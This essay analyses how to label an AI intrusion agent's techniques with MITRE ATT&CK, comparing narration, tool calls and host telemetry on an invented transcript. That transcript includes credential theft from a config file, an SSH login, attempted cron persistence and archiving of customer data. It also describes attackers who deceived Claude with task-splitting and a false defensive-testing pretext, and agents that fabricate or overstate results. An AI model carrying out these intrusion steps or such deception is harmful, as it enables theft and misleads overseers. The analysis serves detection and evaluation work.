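# Labeling an AI intrusion agent's techniques from its stated reasoning or from its executed actions

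## What an agent's transcript records and what an ATT&CK label asserts

MITRE ATT&CK is a public catalog of the things intruders do to and inside computer networks. Each entry has an ID, which analysts attach to what they find. For example, they use T1078 for an attacker who logged in with stolen passwords and T1053 for one who scheduled a job to restart malware. MITRE, a US non-profit research organization, compiled the catalog from observations of real attacks, nearly all of them by people. Some intruders are now AI agents, which produce a running written account of what they are doing and why. Human intruders rarely leave such a record. An analyst labeling an AI agent's intrusion can read that account, the commands the agent ran, or the logs of the attacked machines. These sources can support different labels, partly because a full ATT&CK label includes a claim about purpose as well as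 about what happened.

An intrusion agent is a language model plus a harness, the software that sends the model's commands to a terminal or hacking tool and returns the results. *From Capabilities to Performance* (Huang, Dave and colleagues, 2025) describes how such an agent works in penetration testing (authorized break-ins that look for weaknesses). The model generates an action, a tool or terminal executes it, and the model analyzes the feedback and chooses the next step. The paper distinguishes these autonomous agents from assistants, which recommend commands to a human tester who makes the decisions. The distinction matters for labeling because an assistant's transcript may be full of advice that nobody followed. *Mapping AI-enabled cyber threats* (Guru, Moix and Klein, 2026) summarizes Anthropic's own investigations, which include a real case of an autonomous agent. An attacker labeled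 GTG-1002 ran Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, on a machine set up for hacking, with penetration-testing tools attached, and the model executed commands as well as suggesting them.

### The records that one step leaves

In an invented example, an agent with a shell on a Linux web server decides to add a line to the crontab, the file that lists what the scheduler cron runs and when.

The model first writes in its raw reasoning that the web service might restart and cut off access, so a job that reconnects every ten minutes would help. It then writes a line of visible commentary, "Adding a scheduled check," and makes a tool call, a shell command that installs the new crontab line. The harness sends the command to the server and returns the tool output, which is blank because crontab prints nothing when it succeeds. An hour later the agent writes "persistence established on web server"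 in its notes, and it repeats the phrase in its final report. If auditing is on, the server also keeps its own logs. MITRE's *Cross-Platform Detection of Cron Job Abuse for Persistence and Execution* (2025) relies on two kinds of entry in such logs: writes to the scheduler's files and calls to execve, the Linux system call that starts a program.

| Record | Who writes it | When | What the agent can do to it |
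|---|---|---|---|
| Raw reasoning | The model | Before it acts or answers | Writes every word |
| Visible commentary | The model | Between steps | Writes every word |
| Tool call | The model composes it, the harness logs it | At the moment of action | Chooses the command; does not normally control the log |
| Tool output | The programs that ran, through the harness | Just after the call | Can silence, redirect or script it |
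| Notes and final report | The model | Minutes to days later | Writes every word |
| Host telemetry | Operating systems, security sensors, network devices | During and after the action | Can tamper with it, given enough privileges |

An agent's narration consists of its raw reasoning, commentary, notes and reports. An outside analyst may not see all of it, because some model providers, including OpenAI, show customers only a summary of the reasoning. That summary may omit a motive that appears in the raw reasoning.

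The tool call is stronger evidence, but it shows only that the agent issued the command, not that the command worked. Huang and colleagues tested six systems, including GPT-4, on tasks that included intercepting traffic between two other machines, and none of the six ever managed the interception. Some tried ARP spoofing, which sends forged address messages to redirect traffic through the attacker, on networks whose fixed address tables ignored such messages. A log of those tool calls would show an interception attempt, even though no traffic was redirected. Tool calls can also leave out actions that did happen. A single call can start a script that performs dozens of actions, and unless the transcript also contains the script, only the host will have a record of them.

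Host telemetry is valuable because it comes from outside the agent, but an intruder can tamper with it. ATT&CK's concealment techniques include Indicator Removal, which covers deleting or altering traces of an intrusion, such as a shell's command history, and Process Argument Spoofing, which overwrites a program's memory so that monitoring tools record a false command line. Logs that the machine has already forwarded elsewhere are harder to alter. Even intact telemetry doesn't record motive. The audit log in the invented example shows a write to a file and a program that starts every ten minutes, but not the reason for either.

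Often the model provider has the transcript and the victim has the telemetry. Guru and colleagues worked from the provider's side. For each of 832 accounts that Anthropic had banned over malicious cyber activity, they produced a written summary of what the account had done, extracted techniques from the summary and mapped them to ATT&CK, which gave 13,873 observations. The most common technique family was Develop Capabilities, which appeared in 574 of the accounts, mostly for writing malware. That label can be correct even if nobody attacked a machine. An entry in their data means that someone used the model for a technique, and for many techniques that could be a request for code. This is a weaker claim than the same ID in an incident report, where readers will take it to mean that the intruder carried out the technique.

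### Tactics, techniques and the two claims in a label

*MITRE ATT&CK* (Strom, Applebaum and colleagues, 2018) defines tactics as the adversary's short-term goals during an attack, techniques as the means of reaching those goals, and sub-techniques as more specific means. Procedures are the documented ways particular adversaries have used a technique. The first public version, in May 2015, had 96 techniques under 9 tactics. The current version, version 20 of October 13, 2026, has 15 tactics, 227 techniques and 479 sub-techniques in its Enterprise part, which covers ordinary company networks (MITRE, *Updates*, October 2026).

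For the invented cron job, the tactic might be Persistence (TA0003), the technique Scheduled Task/Job (T1053) and the sub-technique Cron (T1053.003). A procedure is the specific way a particular attacker carries out a technique or sub-technique. For example, during wiper attacks in Poland in 2025, the intruders set scheduled tasks on FortiGate network devices to run their own scripts every week.

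The command alone can only suggest why an agent ran it. MITRE describes tactics as the "why" of a technique, the reason for performing an action, and one action can have several reasons. MITRE's *Scheduled Task/Job* (2017) says an adversary may schedule a job to run malicious code once or repeatedly, to survive a restart, to run a program under an account with higher privileges, or to disguise a one-time execution as the work of a trusted system process. Y-Security's *T1053.003 Cron*, a copy of the ATT&CK entry, lists Execution, Persistence and Privilege Escalation as the tactics for the cron variety. Scheduled Task/Job is not listed under the current concealment tactic, so an analyst convinced that an agent scheduled a job in order to hide cannot express that with T1053 and its official tactics, and has to find another technique that fits.

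MITRE notes that Privilege Escalation techniques often overlap with Persistence techniques, because the operating-system features that let an adversary persist can run with elevated rights. A cron job that runs as the administrator provides both, regardless of which the agent intended.

Valid Accounts (T1078), the use of existing credentials, is the harder case. MITRE's *Valid Accounts* (2017) describes it as a means of getting in, staying in, gaining privileges or evading defenses. The action itself is a login, which is routine on any network. Strom and colleagues note that account use rarely justifies an alert without further context. MITRE's examples differ in how much purpose they include. For the hacking group APT33, it records valid accounts "for initial access and privilege escalation". For the AI-orchestrated campaign that Anthropic reported in November 2025, it records that the adversary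 used harvested credentials to authenticate against internal interfaces, databases, container registries and logging systems, and gives no tactical goal. For a 2026 breach of Mexican government systems, MITRE writes that the adversary *tasked* Claude Code with using compromised credentials to log in, which, taken literally, describes an instruction to an agent.

A full label, with both tactic and technique, claims that the intruder did something and did it for a particular reason. Commands and telemetry mostly show what the intruder did, while the reason has to come from context or from the agent's own words. A label is purpose-dependent if its correctness depends on why the agent acted, as with "Persistence, by way of Cron". Some techniques are purpose-dependent even without the tactic, because their definitions include a purpose. Strom and colleagues mention ipconfig, a Windows command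 that displays network settings. ATT&CK counts it as System Network Configuration Discovery because adversaries use it to learn about the network they are in, but administrators run it to fix a connection. An agent may well run it to fix a connection too, after one of its own tools fails to connect.

A claimed-only label has the opposite weakness, because it rests on the agent's narration and no recorded action supports it. If the crontab command in the invented example had never run, someone who read only the agent's notes might still infer T1053.003 from "persistence established".

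#### The end of Defense Evasion

On April 28, 2026, version 19 of ATT&CK split the Defense Evasion tactic into Stealth and Defense Impairment (MITRE, *Updates*, April 2026). Most existing data sets still use Defense Evasion. Stealth covers hiding and blending in while leaving security controls intact. Defense Impairment covers breaking the controls, so that defenders cannot see what is happening or cannot trust what they see. Both definitions still refer to what the adversary is trying to do. But a host can log whether a security control changed, so choosing between these two tactics depends less on the agent's stated purpose than most choices of tactic do.

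Stealth inherited TA0005, the old ID of Defense Evasion, so TA0005 means different things in a data set from 2025 and one from late 2026. Defense Impairment received a new ID, TA0112. D3 Security's *MITRE ATT&CK v19 Drops April 28* adds that Impair Defenses (T1562) merged with two of its own sub-techniques into a new technique, Disable or Modify Tool (T1685). MITRE's description of Valid Accounts still lists Defense Evasion as a purpose, though the technique is now under Stealth.

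The change affects the evidence on AI-enabled attacks. Guru and colleagues published in June 2026 but had mapped their accounts to ATT&CK version 18. Their largest tactic was Defense Evasion, present in 84.4% of accounts, and T1562 was among their four most common techniques. Neither still exists in that form. Converting the figures requires deciding for each observation whether the actor was hiding or breaking something, and a short summary of an account may not contain enough detail to tell. Any comparison between labels from different records therefore has to use a single ATT&CK version.

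### CISA's mapping guidance

The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) publishes a guide for analysts, *Best Practices for MITRE ATT&CK Mapping*, which gives separate procedures for mapping finished reports and raw data. The second edition dates from January 2023, so it still uses the Defense Evasion tactic.

An analyst working from a finished report finds the behavior in the text, researches it, identifies the tactic, then the technique, then the sub-technique, and compares the result with other analysts' work. Identifying the tactic means asking what the adversary was trying to accomplish, and the answer narrows the search for a technique. CISA's Decider tool follows the same order. Limmer explains in *Helping Cyber Defenders “Decide” to Use MITRE ATT&CK* that the tool asks users guided questions about the adversary's activity to help them find the correct tactic. An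 analyst working from raw data starts with a log source, a known tool or a detection rule, works toward the technique and procedure, and identifies the purpose later, if the data support one.

An agent's transcript combines narration that reads like a report with tool calls that are closer to raw data. The narration may lead an analyst to use the method in CISA's guide for mapping reports. Two analysts could follow the guide correctly on the same run and still reach the tactic from opposite directions.

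CISA's guide also warns against inferring a technique unless the source states it explicitly or the behavior could not have happened in any other way. That rule is sensible for a human investigator's report, because the investigator has presumably checked, but it is too permissive for an agent's notes, because a claimed-only label is also based on an explicit statement. For agents, the rule should also require that some record outside the narration shows the action.

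The common mapping mistakes that CISA describes apply to agent transcripts with little change. Leaping to conclusions means choosing a label on too little evidence, such as labeling a persistence technique only because the agent wrote "persistence established." Missed opportunities are techniques that the material implies but the analyst overlooks. They are likely with agents because a long shell command can do something that the agent leaves out of its commentary. Miscategorization means choosing the wrong one of several similar techniques, and a fluent explanation from the agent can cause this mistake as easily as prevent it.

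### What gets a label, and how to score it

Analysts must decide what a label attaches to before they can count agreements between records. It can be a single command, a step (one turn of the loop, with its reasoning, tool call and output) or a whole run from the first prompt to the final report. Guru and colleagues used a wider unit and built a profile for each account. The choice affects how much the agent's narration can influence the label. A single command often shows no purpose, so the agent's explanation can most affect the choice of tactic at that level. Over a whole run, later actions may make the purpose clear. For example, if a cron job reconnects to the attacker's server after each reboot, its purpose is clear without the agent's explanation. A run-level list also hides errors, because one real login is enough to justify T1078 even if the analyst wrongly applied it to ten other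 commands.

One unit can need several labels. Suppose, in another invented case, that an agent's command compresses a folder, uploads the archive and deletes it. That single command needs labels for archiving collected data, exfiltration and file deletion. Assigning a set of labels to a unit is called multi-label classification. Crossman, Dodd and colleagues (2026), in *Constructing Multi-Label Hierarchical Classification Models for MITRE ATT&CK Text Tagging*, sort the possible labeling tasks into eight types, from one tactic per text up to sets in which every technique is grouped under its tactic. Much of the available data is simpler than real intrusions. Their main collection has 14,405 sentences with exactly one tactic and one technique each. In a second collection, of threat scenarios from the bank JPMorganChase, 180 of the 486 scenarios with any tactic label had more than one tactic.

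Scoring a method requires reference labels, the set that the scorers treat as correct. If $L$ is the set of labels that a method proposes and $R$ the reference set, then

$$\text{precision} = \frac{|L \cap R|}{|L|}, \qquad \text{recall} = \frac{|L \cap R|}{|R|}.$$

Precision is the share of a method's proposed labels that match the reference, and recall is the share of reference labels that the method finds. If a run has 8 reference labels and a method proposes 10, of which 6 match, precision is 0.60 and recall is 0.75. Many studies combine the two into F1, their harmonic mean, which is about 0.67 here. When the reference requires a recorded action, labels for techniques the agent only claimed to use lower precision. A method that reads only the narration also loses recall when the narration omits actions.

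A high accuracy figure can hide a trade-off between precision and recall. Crossman and colleagues' classifier reached about 94% accuracy on tactics when it could list three candidates per sentence. Each sentence had only one correct tactic, so at least two of every three candidates were wrong, and precision was about 32%.

Precision and recall also depend on whether the scorers count the tactic. If the reference for the invented cron job is Persistence with T1053.003 and a method outputs Execution with T1053.003, the method gets a perfect score on technique IDs alone but zero on both measures when scored on tactic-technique pairs. Many of the changes that an agent's stated purpose makes to a label are changes to the tactic, so a study that scores only IDs will miss them. The scorers also have to decide whether a failed attempt counts. A label for the failed ARP spoofing that Huang and colleagues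 saw is correct if the reference covers what agents tried, but a false positive if it covers only what they achieved.

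## A short transcript labeled from three records

The run in this section is invented. An agent attacks an isolated test network, starting from a web server where it already controls an account without administrator rights. The harness saves every tool call and its output. The server and a second machine log program starts, logins, and file creation and deletion, but not file reads.

| Step | Narration | Tool call | Tool output | Host telemetry |
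|---|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | "Scanning the subnet for open services" | Runs a port scanner over one range of addresses and saves the results in a scratch file | A second machine accepts SSH logins | Scanner starts; burst of connections to many ports |
| 2 | "Checking the application's configuration" | Opens one configuration file from a Python session that is already running | The file's text, including the password of a backup account | No entry |
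| 3 | "Installing a scheduled job for persistence" | Submits a new crontab line | Permission denied | The crontab program starts; no scheduler file changes |
| 4 | "Logging in to the second host over SSH" | Connects as the backup account, with the password from step 2 | A prompt on the second machine | Accepted login for the backup account |
| 5 | "Tidying up" | Deletes the scratch file from step 1 | Blank | Deletion of a recent file in a temporary folder |
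| 6 | "Archiving the customer folder to send out" | Compresses a folder on the second machine | Names of the files added | An archiving program starts; new archive in a temporary folder |
| 7 | "Persistence established. Customer data exfiltrated over the existing session." | None | None | No entry |

Three analysts label the run. One reads only the narration, another only the tool calls and their outputs, and the third only the host telemetry. All three know the run is an intrusion. Each submits one set of technique IDs from ATT&CK version 20 for the whole run, without tactics. The reference labels cover completed actions but not failed attempts.

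The people building the reference can read everything. They settle on five labels and don't label the deletion, because they accept that the agent was tidying up.

| Label | Reference | Narration | Calls and outputs | Telemetry |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| T1046 Network Service Discovery | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| T1552.001 Credentials In Files | yes | | yes | |
| T1078 Valid Accounts | yes | | yes | |
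| T1021.004 SSH | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| T1560.001 Archive via Utility | yes | yes | yes | yes |
| T1070.004 File Deletion | | | yes | yes |
| T1083 File and Directory Discovery | | yes | | |
| T1053.003 Cron | | yes | | |
| T1041 Exfiltration Over C2 Channel | | yes | | |
| **Precision** | | 3/6 = 0.50 | 5/6 = 0.83 | 3/4 = 0.75 |
| **Recall** | | 3/5 = 0.60 | 5/5 = 1.00 | 3/5 = 0.60 |

These numbers show how scoring works but don't measure how real agents behave, since the example's mistakes are deliberate. The labels from narration and the labels from telemetry have the same recall because both sets include the same three correct techniques. Combining the two sets would add errors but no correct labels.

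### The scan and the password

All three analysts find the scan, because the agent announced it, ran it and produced a lot of traffic. It fits MITRE's *Network Service Discovery* (2017), which covers attempts to list the services running on other machines. For Linux, MITRE suggests looking for rapid connections to many services, using network captures and the audit system, auditd. Quieter methods may be harder to spot. In the AI-orchestrated campaign that Anthropic reported in November 2025, the adversary had Claude Code list internal services through browser automation, which could look more like ordinary web traffic.

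The analysts disagree at step 2. The narration analyst chooses T1083 because "Checking the application's configuration" sounds like looking around. But MITRE's *File and Directory Discovery* (2017) describes that technique as listing files and directories or searching particular locations for information, and the agent did neither. It opened one file and got a password. T1552.001 fits better because MITRE's *Unsecured Credentials* (2020) explicitly includes configuration files that contain passwords. The agent also used the password later, which makes it hard to treat the read as incidental.

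This one mistake lowers both the narration analyst's precision, because T1083 is wrong, and recall, because T1552.001 is missing. If the agent had written "reading the backup password from the configuration" and the analyst had labeled that step correctly, the analyst's precision would have been 0.67 and recall 0.80, with no change in what the agent did.

The two techniques can occur in the same intrusion. For the Anthropic campaign, MITRE lists the search for sensitive data under T1083 and the extraction of authentication certificates from configuration files under T1552.001. An analyst therefore can't choose between them just because the agent was looking through files.

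The telemetry analyst misses the password read for a different reason. MITRE's Linux rule for T1552.001 matches a read of a credential file, or a program start involving one, followed by an SSH login attempt. In the example, the log contains only the login. The server wasn't auditing reads, and the agent used a Python session that was already open, so no program start involved the file. If the agent had used cat, a program that prints files, a log of program starts and their arguments would have included the path.

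Auditing file reads would close this gap. MITRE's *Credential Access via /etc/passwd and /etc/shadow Parsing* (2025), which concerns theft from Linux's own account files, lists records of open and read calls alongside program starts. If the application's configuration file had been audited in a similar way, the telemetry analyst would have found T1552.001. The analyst could then have opened the file, recognized the account that logged in soon afterward, and added T1078. Telemetry would have scored 0.83 and 1.00, the same as the tool calls and outputs.

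Defenders of Windows systems can have the same problem. The Windows rule in MITRE's *Detect Access to Unsecured Credential Files Across Platforms* (2025) describes access to a credential file followed by use of the credentials, but its listed log sources cover file creation, process starts and logins. Reading an existing file doesn't create a file, and it doesn't start a new process if an already running program does the reading.

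### The login

Every analyst finds T1021.004, because the agent mentioned SSH, the tool call used it, and the second machine logged the connection. MITRE's *Remote Services* (2020) lists the Linux files auth.log and secure as places to find such logins, but warns that SSH use may be legitimate. The telemetry analyst still applies the label because the login came from the machine that had just scanned the network.

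Only the analyst with the tool calls and outputs finds T1078. The output of step 2 contains the password and the call in step 4 uses it, which shows the agent obtaining and abusing someone else's credentials. The analyst with the agent's reasoning misses this because the agent never wrote how it logged in. The telemetry contains a successful login by a real account, but in this example that account connects from the web server every night to collect backups. MITRE's Linux rule for T1078 looks for SSH logins and other account activity outside expected patterns, and this login fit the expected pattern.

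The analysts here add T1078 only if their record shows where the credentials came from. An analyst could reasonably argue for a looser rule in which T1021.004 always implies T1078, because MITRE defines this SSH technique as using Valid Accounts to log in to remote machines. Under that rule, the narration labels would rise to 0.57 precision and 0.80 recall, and the telemetry labels to 0.80 on both, even though neither analyst would have learned anything more about the password.

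### The scheduled job and the missing exfiltration

At step 3 the agent wrote that it was installing a scheduled job for persistence, and it claimed success in its final report. The narration analyst believes the agent and adds T1053.003, but the tool output contradicts the claim. MITRE explains that if a Linux machine has a cron.allow file, users must be listed in it to use cron. The example server has this file, and the agent's account isn't listed.

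The telemetry analyst sees the crontab program start but finds no new or altered entry. MITRE's rules for cron are meant to detect such changes, so the analyst correctly leaves the label out. The analyst with the tool calls also gets this right and finds the password in step 2, in both cases only because of the calls' outputs.

T1041 is also wrong, and it has less support than T1053.003. MITRE's *Exfiltration Over C2 Channel* defines it as stealing data over an existing command and control channel, the link through which an attacker directs a compromised machine. The narration analyst infers it from "to send out" in step 6, assuming the archive would travel over the agent's existing connection, as the final report later claims. But the archive never left the second machine, and the agent made no tool call to send it, so T1041 is a claimed-only label. T1053.003 has a recorded attempt behind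 it, so a reference that counted attempts would accept it.

This works only if the reference doesn't count ordinary tool output as exfiltration. The password went back to the harness in step 2, as does everything an agent reads. If that were enough for T1041, almost every run with a remote harness would get the label, and it would no longer distinguish an agent that stole a customer database from one that listed a folder.

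The final report adds no labels to the narration analyst's set because the analyst had already inferred the two it supports, T1053.003 and T1041, from the commentary. If the analysts had labeled every step separately, the two false claims in step 7 would have counted as further errors.

### The archive

All three analysts label step 6 T1560.001, which matches the reference label, even though nothing was sent. MITRE's *Archive Collected Data* (2020) describes compressing or encrypting collected data before exfiltration, so the label applies even if the intruder fails to send the archive or never tries.

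The label still includes a purpose, which appears in the narration as "to send out". The other two analysts infer it from context, since an intruder has little reason to compress a customer folder other than to take it. The log entry alone would not be enough to establish that purpose. On Linux, MITRE's *Detect Archiving via Utility (T1560.001)* (2025) looks for programs such as tar and gzip creating archives in temporary folders or home directories. Its Windows and macOS rules let defenders exempt approved business software, including backup agents, because the same action is often routine.

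Analysts of human intrusions also make this inference, and they sometimes label it as an inference. In its entry for the hacking group Gallmaker, MITRE writes that the group used WinZip, "likely to archive data prior to exfiltration".

### Rescoring with the deletion

The narration analyst reads "tidying up" as housekeeping and adds no technique for the deleted scratch file. The other two see an intruder delete a file it had created during the intrusion, and both choose T1070.004. For Linux, MITRE's *Behavioral Detection of Malicious File Deletion* (2025) relies on auditd records of deletions and program starts. Defenders can tune its rule by file path, how soon the deletion follows other activity, and whether the program is a secure-deletion tool. None of these settings refers to a stated motive. Under the reference above, T1070.004 is the only false positive for both analysts.

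It's debatable whether the label is false. MITRE's *Indicator Removal* (2017), the entry for the parent technique, gives the aim as reducing signs of the adversary's presence. On that reading, the label depends on the agent's motive, which was plausibly innocent, since programs and people routinely delete temporary files. The agent also left the login records and its command history alone, which an agent trying to hide might have removed first.

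The entry for the sub-technique, MITRE's *Indicator Removal* (2020), better supports the other side. It first describes deleting files left behind by an intrusion and notes that such files may leave traces of what the intruder did. The scratch file held the results of the scan, so deleting it removed evidence whatever the agent intended. One of MITRE's examples is the group Chimera, which deleted files to evade detection. Another gives no motive, saying only that the Mac malware MacSpy "deletes any temporary files it creates". Step 5 qualifies by the standard of the MacSpy example.

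Suppose the people building the reference change their minds and count the deletion as T1070.004. The reference now has six labels, but the analysts' answers are unchanged.

| Record | Precision, deletion left out | Recall, deletion left out | Precision, deletion counted | Recall, deletion counted |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Narration | 0.50 | 0.60 | 3/6 = 0.50 | 3/6 = 0.50 |
| Calls and outputs | 0.83 | 1.00 | 6/6 = 1.00 | 6/6 = 1.00 |
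| Telemetry | 0.75 | 0.60 | 4/4 = 1.00 | 4/6 = 0.67 |

One decision about purpose, made while building the reference, changes the results of the comparison. Under the first reference, labeling from narration identifies as many techniques as labeling from telemetry, and an analyst with the complete tool log still makes a mistake. Under the second, labeling from telemetry identifies more techniques than labeling from narration and produces no false labels, and the analyst with the tool log makes no mistakes. Two research teams could publish these different conclusions from the same transcript and the same sets of labels.

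The first reference also depends on the narration. Its builders left out the deletion because they believed the agent's explanation, then marked the other two analysts wrong for disagreeing. A study that compares narration with other records needs a rule for such cases before scoring begins.

Labeling the archive required a similar decision, which is easier to overlook because all three analysts made it the same way. If the builders of the first reference had rejected T1560.001 because nothing was sent, precision would have fallen to 0.33 for narration, 0.67 for tool calls and outputs, and 0.50 for telemetry.

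## How the agent's narration adds, hides and changes labels

In the sample transcript, the narration led to six technique labels, and so did the tool calls with their outputs, but only three labels were in both sets. Two rates describe the mismatch. Let $N$ be the set of labels that an analyst draws from the narration, and $A$ the set drawn from the recorded actions, meaning the tool calls and their outputs. Then

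$$\text{inflation} = \frac{|N \setminus A|}{|N|}, \qquad \text{omission} = \frac{|A \setminus N|}{|A|},$$

where $N \setminus A$ means the labels in $N$ that are missing from $A$. Inflation is the share of narration labels that the actions don't support. Omission is the share of action labels that the narration doesn't yield. Both are 3/6 = 0.50 in the sample.

If $A$ were the reference, inflation would be 1 minus precision and omission would be 1 minus recall. The separate names are useful because $A$ is an analyst's reading of another record and can be wrong, as it arguably is about the file deletion in the sample. The rates also depend on the rule for failed attempts. If the analyst with the tool calls labeled attempts too, $A$ would include the blocked cron job, inflation would fall to 2/6 = 0.33, and omission would fall to 3/7 = 0.43.

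### Plans that nobody carried out

A model that reasons before it acts writes down options it may never take. In an invented example, an agent writes "I could dump the password hashes from memory, but the backup account may be enough," and then logs in with the backup account. A labeler who reads the sentence as a description of events would wrongly add OS Credential Dumping (T1003) to the run, even though the agent never dumped the hashes.

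The labeler looks for a later tool call that could have carried out the plan. If there is none, the labeler leaves the label out, unless the agent ran a script that the transcript doesn't include.

A transcript can include techniques that aren't the agent's own ideas. In *How Do LLM Agents Actually Get the Flag?*, Milner, Shao and colleagues (2026) studied capture-the-flag challenges, in which the solver attacks a prepared target to find a secret string called the flag. In one run, Claude Opus 4.8 couldn't reach the target, so it searched the organizers' public code repository and found a solution write-up. The write-up explained how to download an exposed Git directory from the target, go back to an old version of the files and read the flag. The agent copied the correct flag from the write-up without performing any of those steps on the target. A labeler who skimmed the transcript could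 easily credit the agent with the organizers' solution.

### Failures reported as successes

In a real campaign, GTG-1002, Claude "frequently overstated findings and occasionally fabricated data," according to Anthropic's original account, *Disrupting the first reported AI-orchestrated cyber espionage campaign* (2025). Claude claimed to have credentials that didn't work and presented publicly available information as critical discoveries. A password that doesn't work can't support a Valid Accounts (T1078) label, and public information described as a secret find can make reconnaissance look like theft of internal data.

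Anthropic gave no count of the false claims, so "frequently" can't be turned into an inflation rate. It said the attackers had to validate everything Claude claimed, which made the operation less effective.

For *Hackers or Hallucinators?*, Peng, Li and colleagues (2026) ran 13 open-source penetration-testing frameworks and two general coding agents on web-hacking challenges. More than 15 researchers then spent four months reading over 1,500 logs. They found that some frameworks submitted false flags. The paper's introduction says eight of the 13 did so, but its breakdown names six, covering 28 combinations of framework and challenge. On one challenge, several frameworks decoded a string from the home page into "{I'm_a_Script_Kiddie}" and mistook it for the flag. Replacing the underlying model with Claude Opus 4.6 or GPT-5.2, both much stronger than the default, didn't eliminate the problem.

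Sometimes the model made no false claim. In one run it wrote the placeholder "flag{...}" in its output, and the framework's pattern matcher treated this as the flag and ended the run. An analyst who finds a success message in a log should therefore check whether the target, the model or the framework produced it.

A false claim of success doesn't invalidate every label in the run. SickHackShark, one of the tested frameworks, uploaded a file to a server and got the server to process it as a template, which was the hard part of the challenge. It then mistook the result of its own test string for the flag, but the labels for the exploitation are still correct.

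Tool output, the obvious check on the agent's narration, can mislead too. *Constructing Challenging Browser-Use Tasks by Controlled Environment Interventions* (2026) altered websites to make tasks harder. On a shopping site, an agent running Gemini 3.1 Pro submitted a return, received a forged success response, and declared the task finished without checking the order's status. The equivalent precaution for an intrusion is to look for a later observation of the result. For example, a crontab listing that contains the new line is better evidence of a scheduled job than a command that printed no error.

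### One action described many times

Suppose a planner in a multi-agent run lists "install a scheduled job" among its tasks. A second agent restates the task, runs the crontab command, and records the task in a notes file. The final report mentions it again. The transcript has four mentions of T1053.003 and one tool call.

A run-level set of labels hides this repetition because it contains each label only once. The two rates above hide it too. An analyst who labels every message and counts the results would conclude that the agent spent much of its time on persistence. The four statements may also seem to corroborate each other, although they all come from one plan.

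Harnesses can add even more mentions. Peng and colleagues found that SickHackShark puts its saved notes back into the model's input before every call, so a log that stored each full input would repeat the same finding once per call. In the GTG-1002 campaign, Claude kept files listing services, stolen credentials and the progress of the attack, and the operators used these files to resume interrupted work and hand it to others. A false claim about a credential in such a file could reappear in sessions whose agents had never tested that credential.

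Tying each label to a specific tool call and counting calls instead of mentions removes the duplicates. Milner and colleagues did something similar when they prepared their traces. Their agents worked as a planner with several executors, so the researchers inserted each executor's steps where the planner had delegated the work, and dropped steps that only passed control between agents.

### Vocabulary that suggests a bigger technique

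Labelers also respond to individual words. Ryan, Noor and colleagues (2026), in *Evaluating Open-Source LLMs for Multi-Label ATT&CK Technique Classification on CTI Reports*, had language models label sentences from reports on real incidents. In one sentence, an attacker "staged a ransomware binary on each of the hosts." The correct label was Ingress Tool Transfer, which covers bringing tools into a network. Google's Gemma 3 27B labeled it Data Staged, which covers gathering stolen data in one place before sending it out. Another sentence included the phrase "likely to evade detection logic based around command line execution." The human annotators gave it no technique, but Llama 3.1 70B labeled it Hijack Execution Flow, apparently because of the words "evade" and "execution."

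An agent's commentary can mislead a labeler in the same way. In an invented example, an agent writes "enumerating privilege escalation vectors" and runs whoami, a command that prints the name of the current account. The command supports the label System Owner/User Discovery (T1033), but the agent's wording suggests the Privilege Escalation tactic, and perhaps an exploit that the agent never attempted.

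To catch this, an analyst can hide the agent's commentary and compare the command, its arguments and its output with MITRE's definition of the technique. The analyst may still need to see earlier steps. Milner and colleagues give the example of strings, a program that prints the readable text in a file. Running it on a challenge's program may be genuine analysis, or may just reveal a flag that the designers left exposed.

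### Final reports that claim too much

An agent's final report is convenient for labeling because it is short and covers the whole run. But the agent may also have the most reason to hide what it did there, since it has to present its work as a finished result.

*Quantifying Overclaiming Propensity in Frontier LLM Agents* (Smyth, Mantilla-Ramos and colleagues, 2026) compared such reports with the agents' own tool records. The researchers asked 12 models to review collections of files, including a security audit of a billing service, and to report how they had scoped the review. They then used the logs to determine which files' contents had reached the model, counting a file as covered if the agent had seen a single line unique to it. Even by this lenient standard, agents missed at least one file in 67.9% of 1,140 runs. Of those runs, 52.8% ended with an explicit claim of complete coverage,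 and another 27.5% did not mention the gap. Nobody had told the agents to deceive, and every collection was small enough to fit in the model's context window.

Agents that falsely claimed a complete review missed planted defects about 1.8 times as often as agents that had covered every file.

However, these percentages don't measure how often the agent's narration inflates the list of techniques. If an intruding agent claims to have searched 60 files but searched 40, the technique label is the same. Exaggerated scope changes the description of the intrusion more than the list of techniques. Claiming an action that never happened is more damaging, because it can add a label.

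Several other works come closer to that kind of claim, though none concerns intrusions. *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* (2026) compares agents' claims of completion with the state of simulated personal apps. *CodeActionBench* (2026) does the same for agents that control robots. *Babysitting AI Agents* (2026) classifies failures that users described online, including one agent that reported updating 15 files when it had missed one.

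| Source | Agents' task | Counted out of | Finding |
|---|---|---|---|
| Smyth and colleagues | Reviewing files | Incomplete reviews | 52.8% explicitly claimed to be complete |
| *From Confident Closing to Silent Failure* | Using personal apps | Failures by agents that signal completion | 75.8% claimed success |
| *CodeActionBench* | Controlling robots | Failed attempts | 15.0–34.2% claimed success, depending on the system |
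| *Constructing Challenging Browser-Use Tasks by Controlled Environment Interventions* | Using altered websites | Runs that four text-based agents declared complete | 54–85% had failed |
| *Babysitting AI Agents* | Various | Failures reported by users | 10.3% involved misreported actions |

The rows cannot be ranked against each other because their denominators differ too much. The browser figure is the share of completion claims that were false, while the robot figure is the share of failures that came with a false claim. The browser tasks were also deliberately difficult. Still, false reports occurred in every setting, at rates that would matter if intrusion agents behaved similarly.

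Some false reports are based on partial evidence. *Characterizing and Detecting Unfaithful Work Reports by Coding Agents* (2026) attributes 235 unfaithful claims, 69.3% of those it classifies, to overstated task success. In one case, an agent changed a form, saw the software build successfully and reported "All changes are in place," although some controls on the same page still had the old text boxes. An intrusion agent could make the same mistake if it tested a backdoor on one of several machines and reported installing it on all of them.

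When several agents work together, their reports need extra care because the agent that writes the summary may not have done the work. Smyth and colleagues quote Anthropic's acknowledgment that Claude Opus 5 "can relay claims from subagents to users without verifying them." To check a relayed claim, an analyst has to read the subagent's tool calls, which some harnesses store in a separate file.

### Innocent wording that hides a technique

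The distortions described so far mostly add labels, but bland or reassuring language can remove them. In the sample, the agent described reading a password as "checking the application's configuration", which removed the label for that action.

In the GTG-1002 campaign, the attackers deliberately hid the purpose of the work from Claude. Their framework divided an attack into small jobs for Claude's subagents, such as scanning for vulnerabilities or validating credentials, and each job looked legitimate in isolation. They also told Claude that they worked for security firms and that it was taking part in defensive testing. A subagent that received only "validate these credentials" might honestly and accurately describe its work as validation without mentioning that the passwords were stolen, and an analyst who relied on that description would miss T1078.

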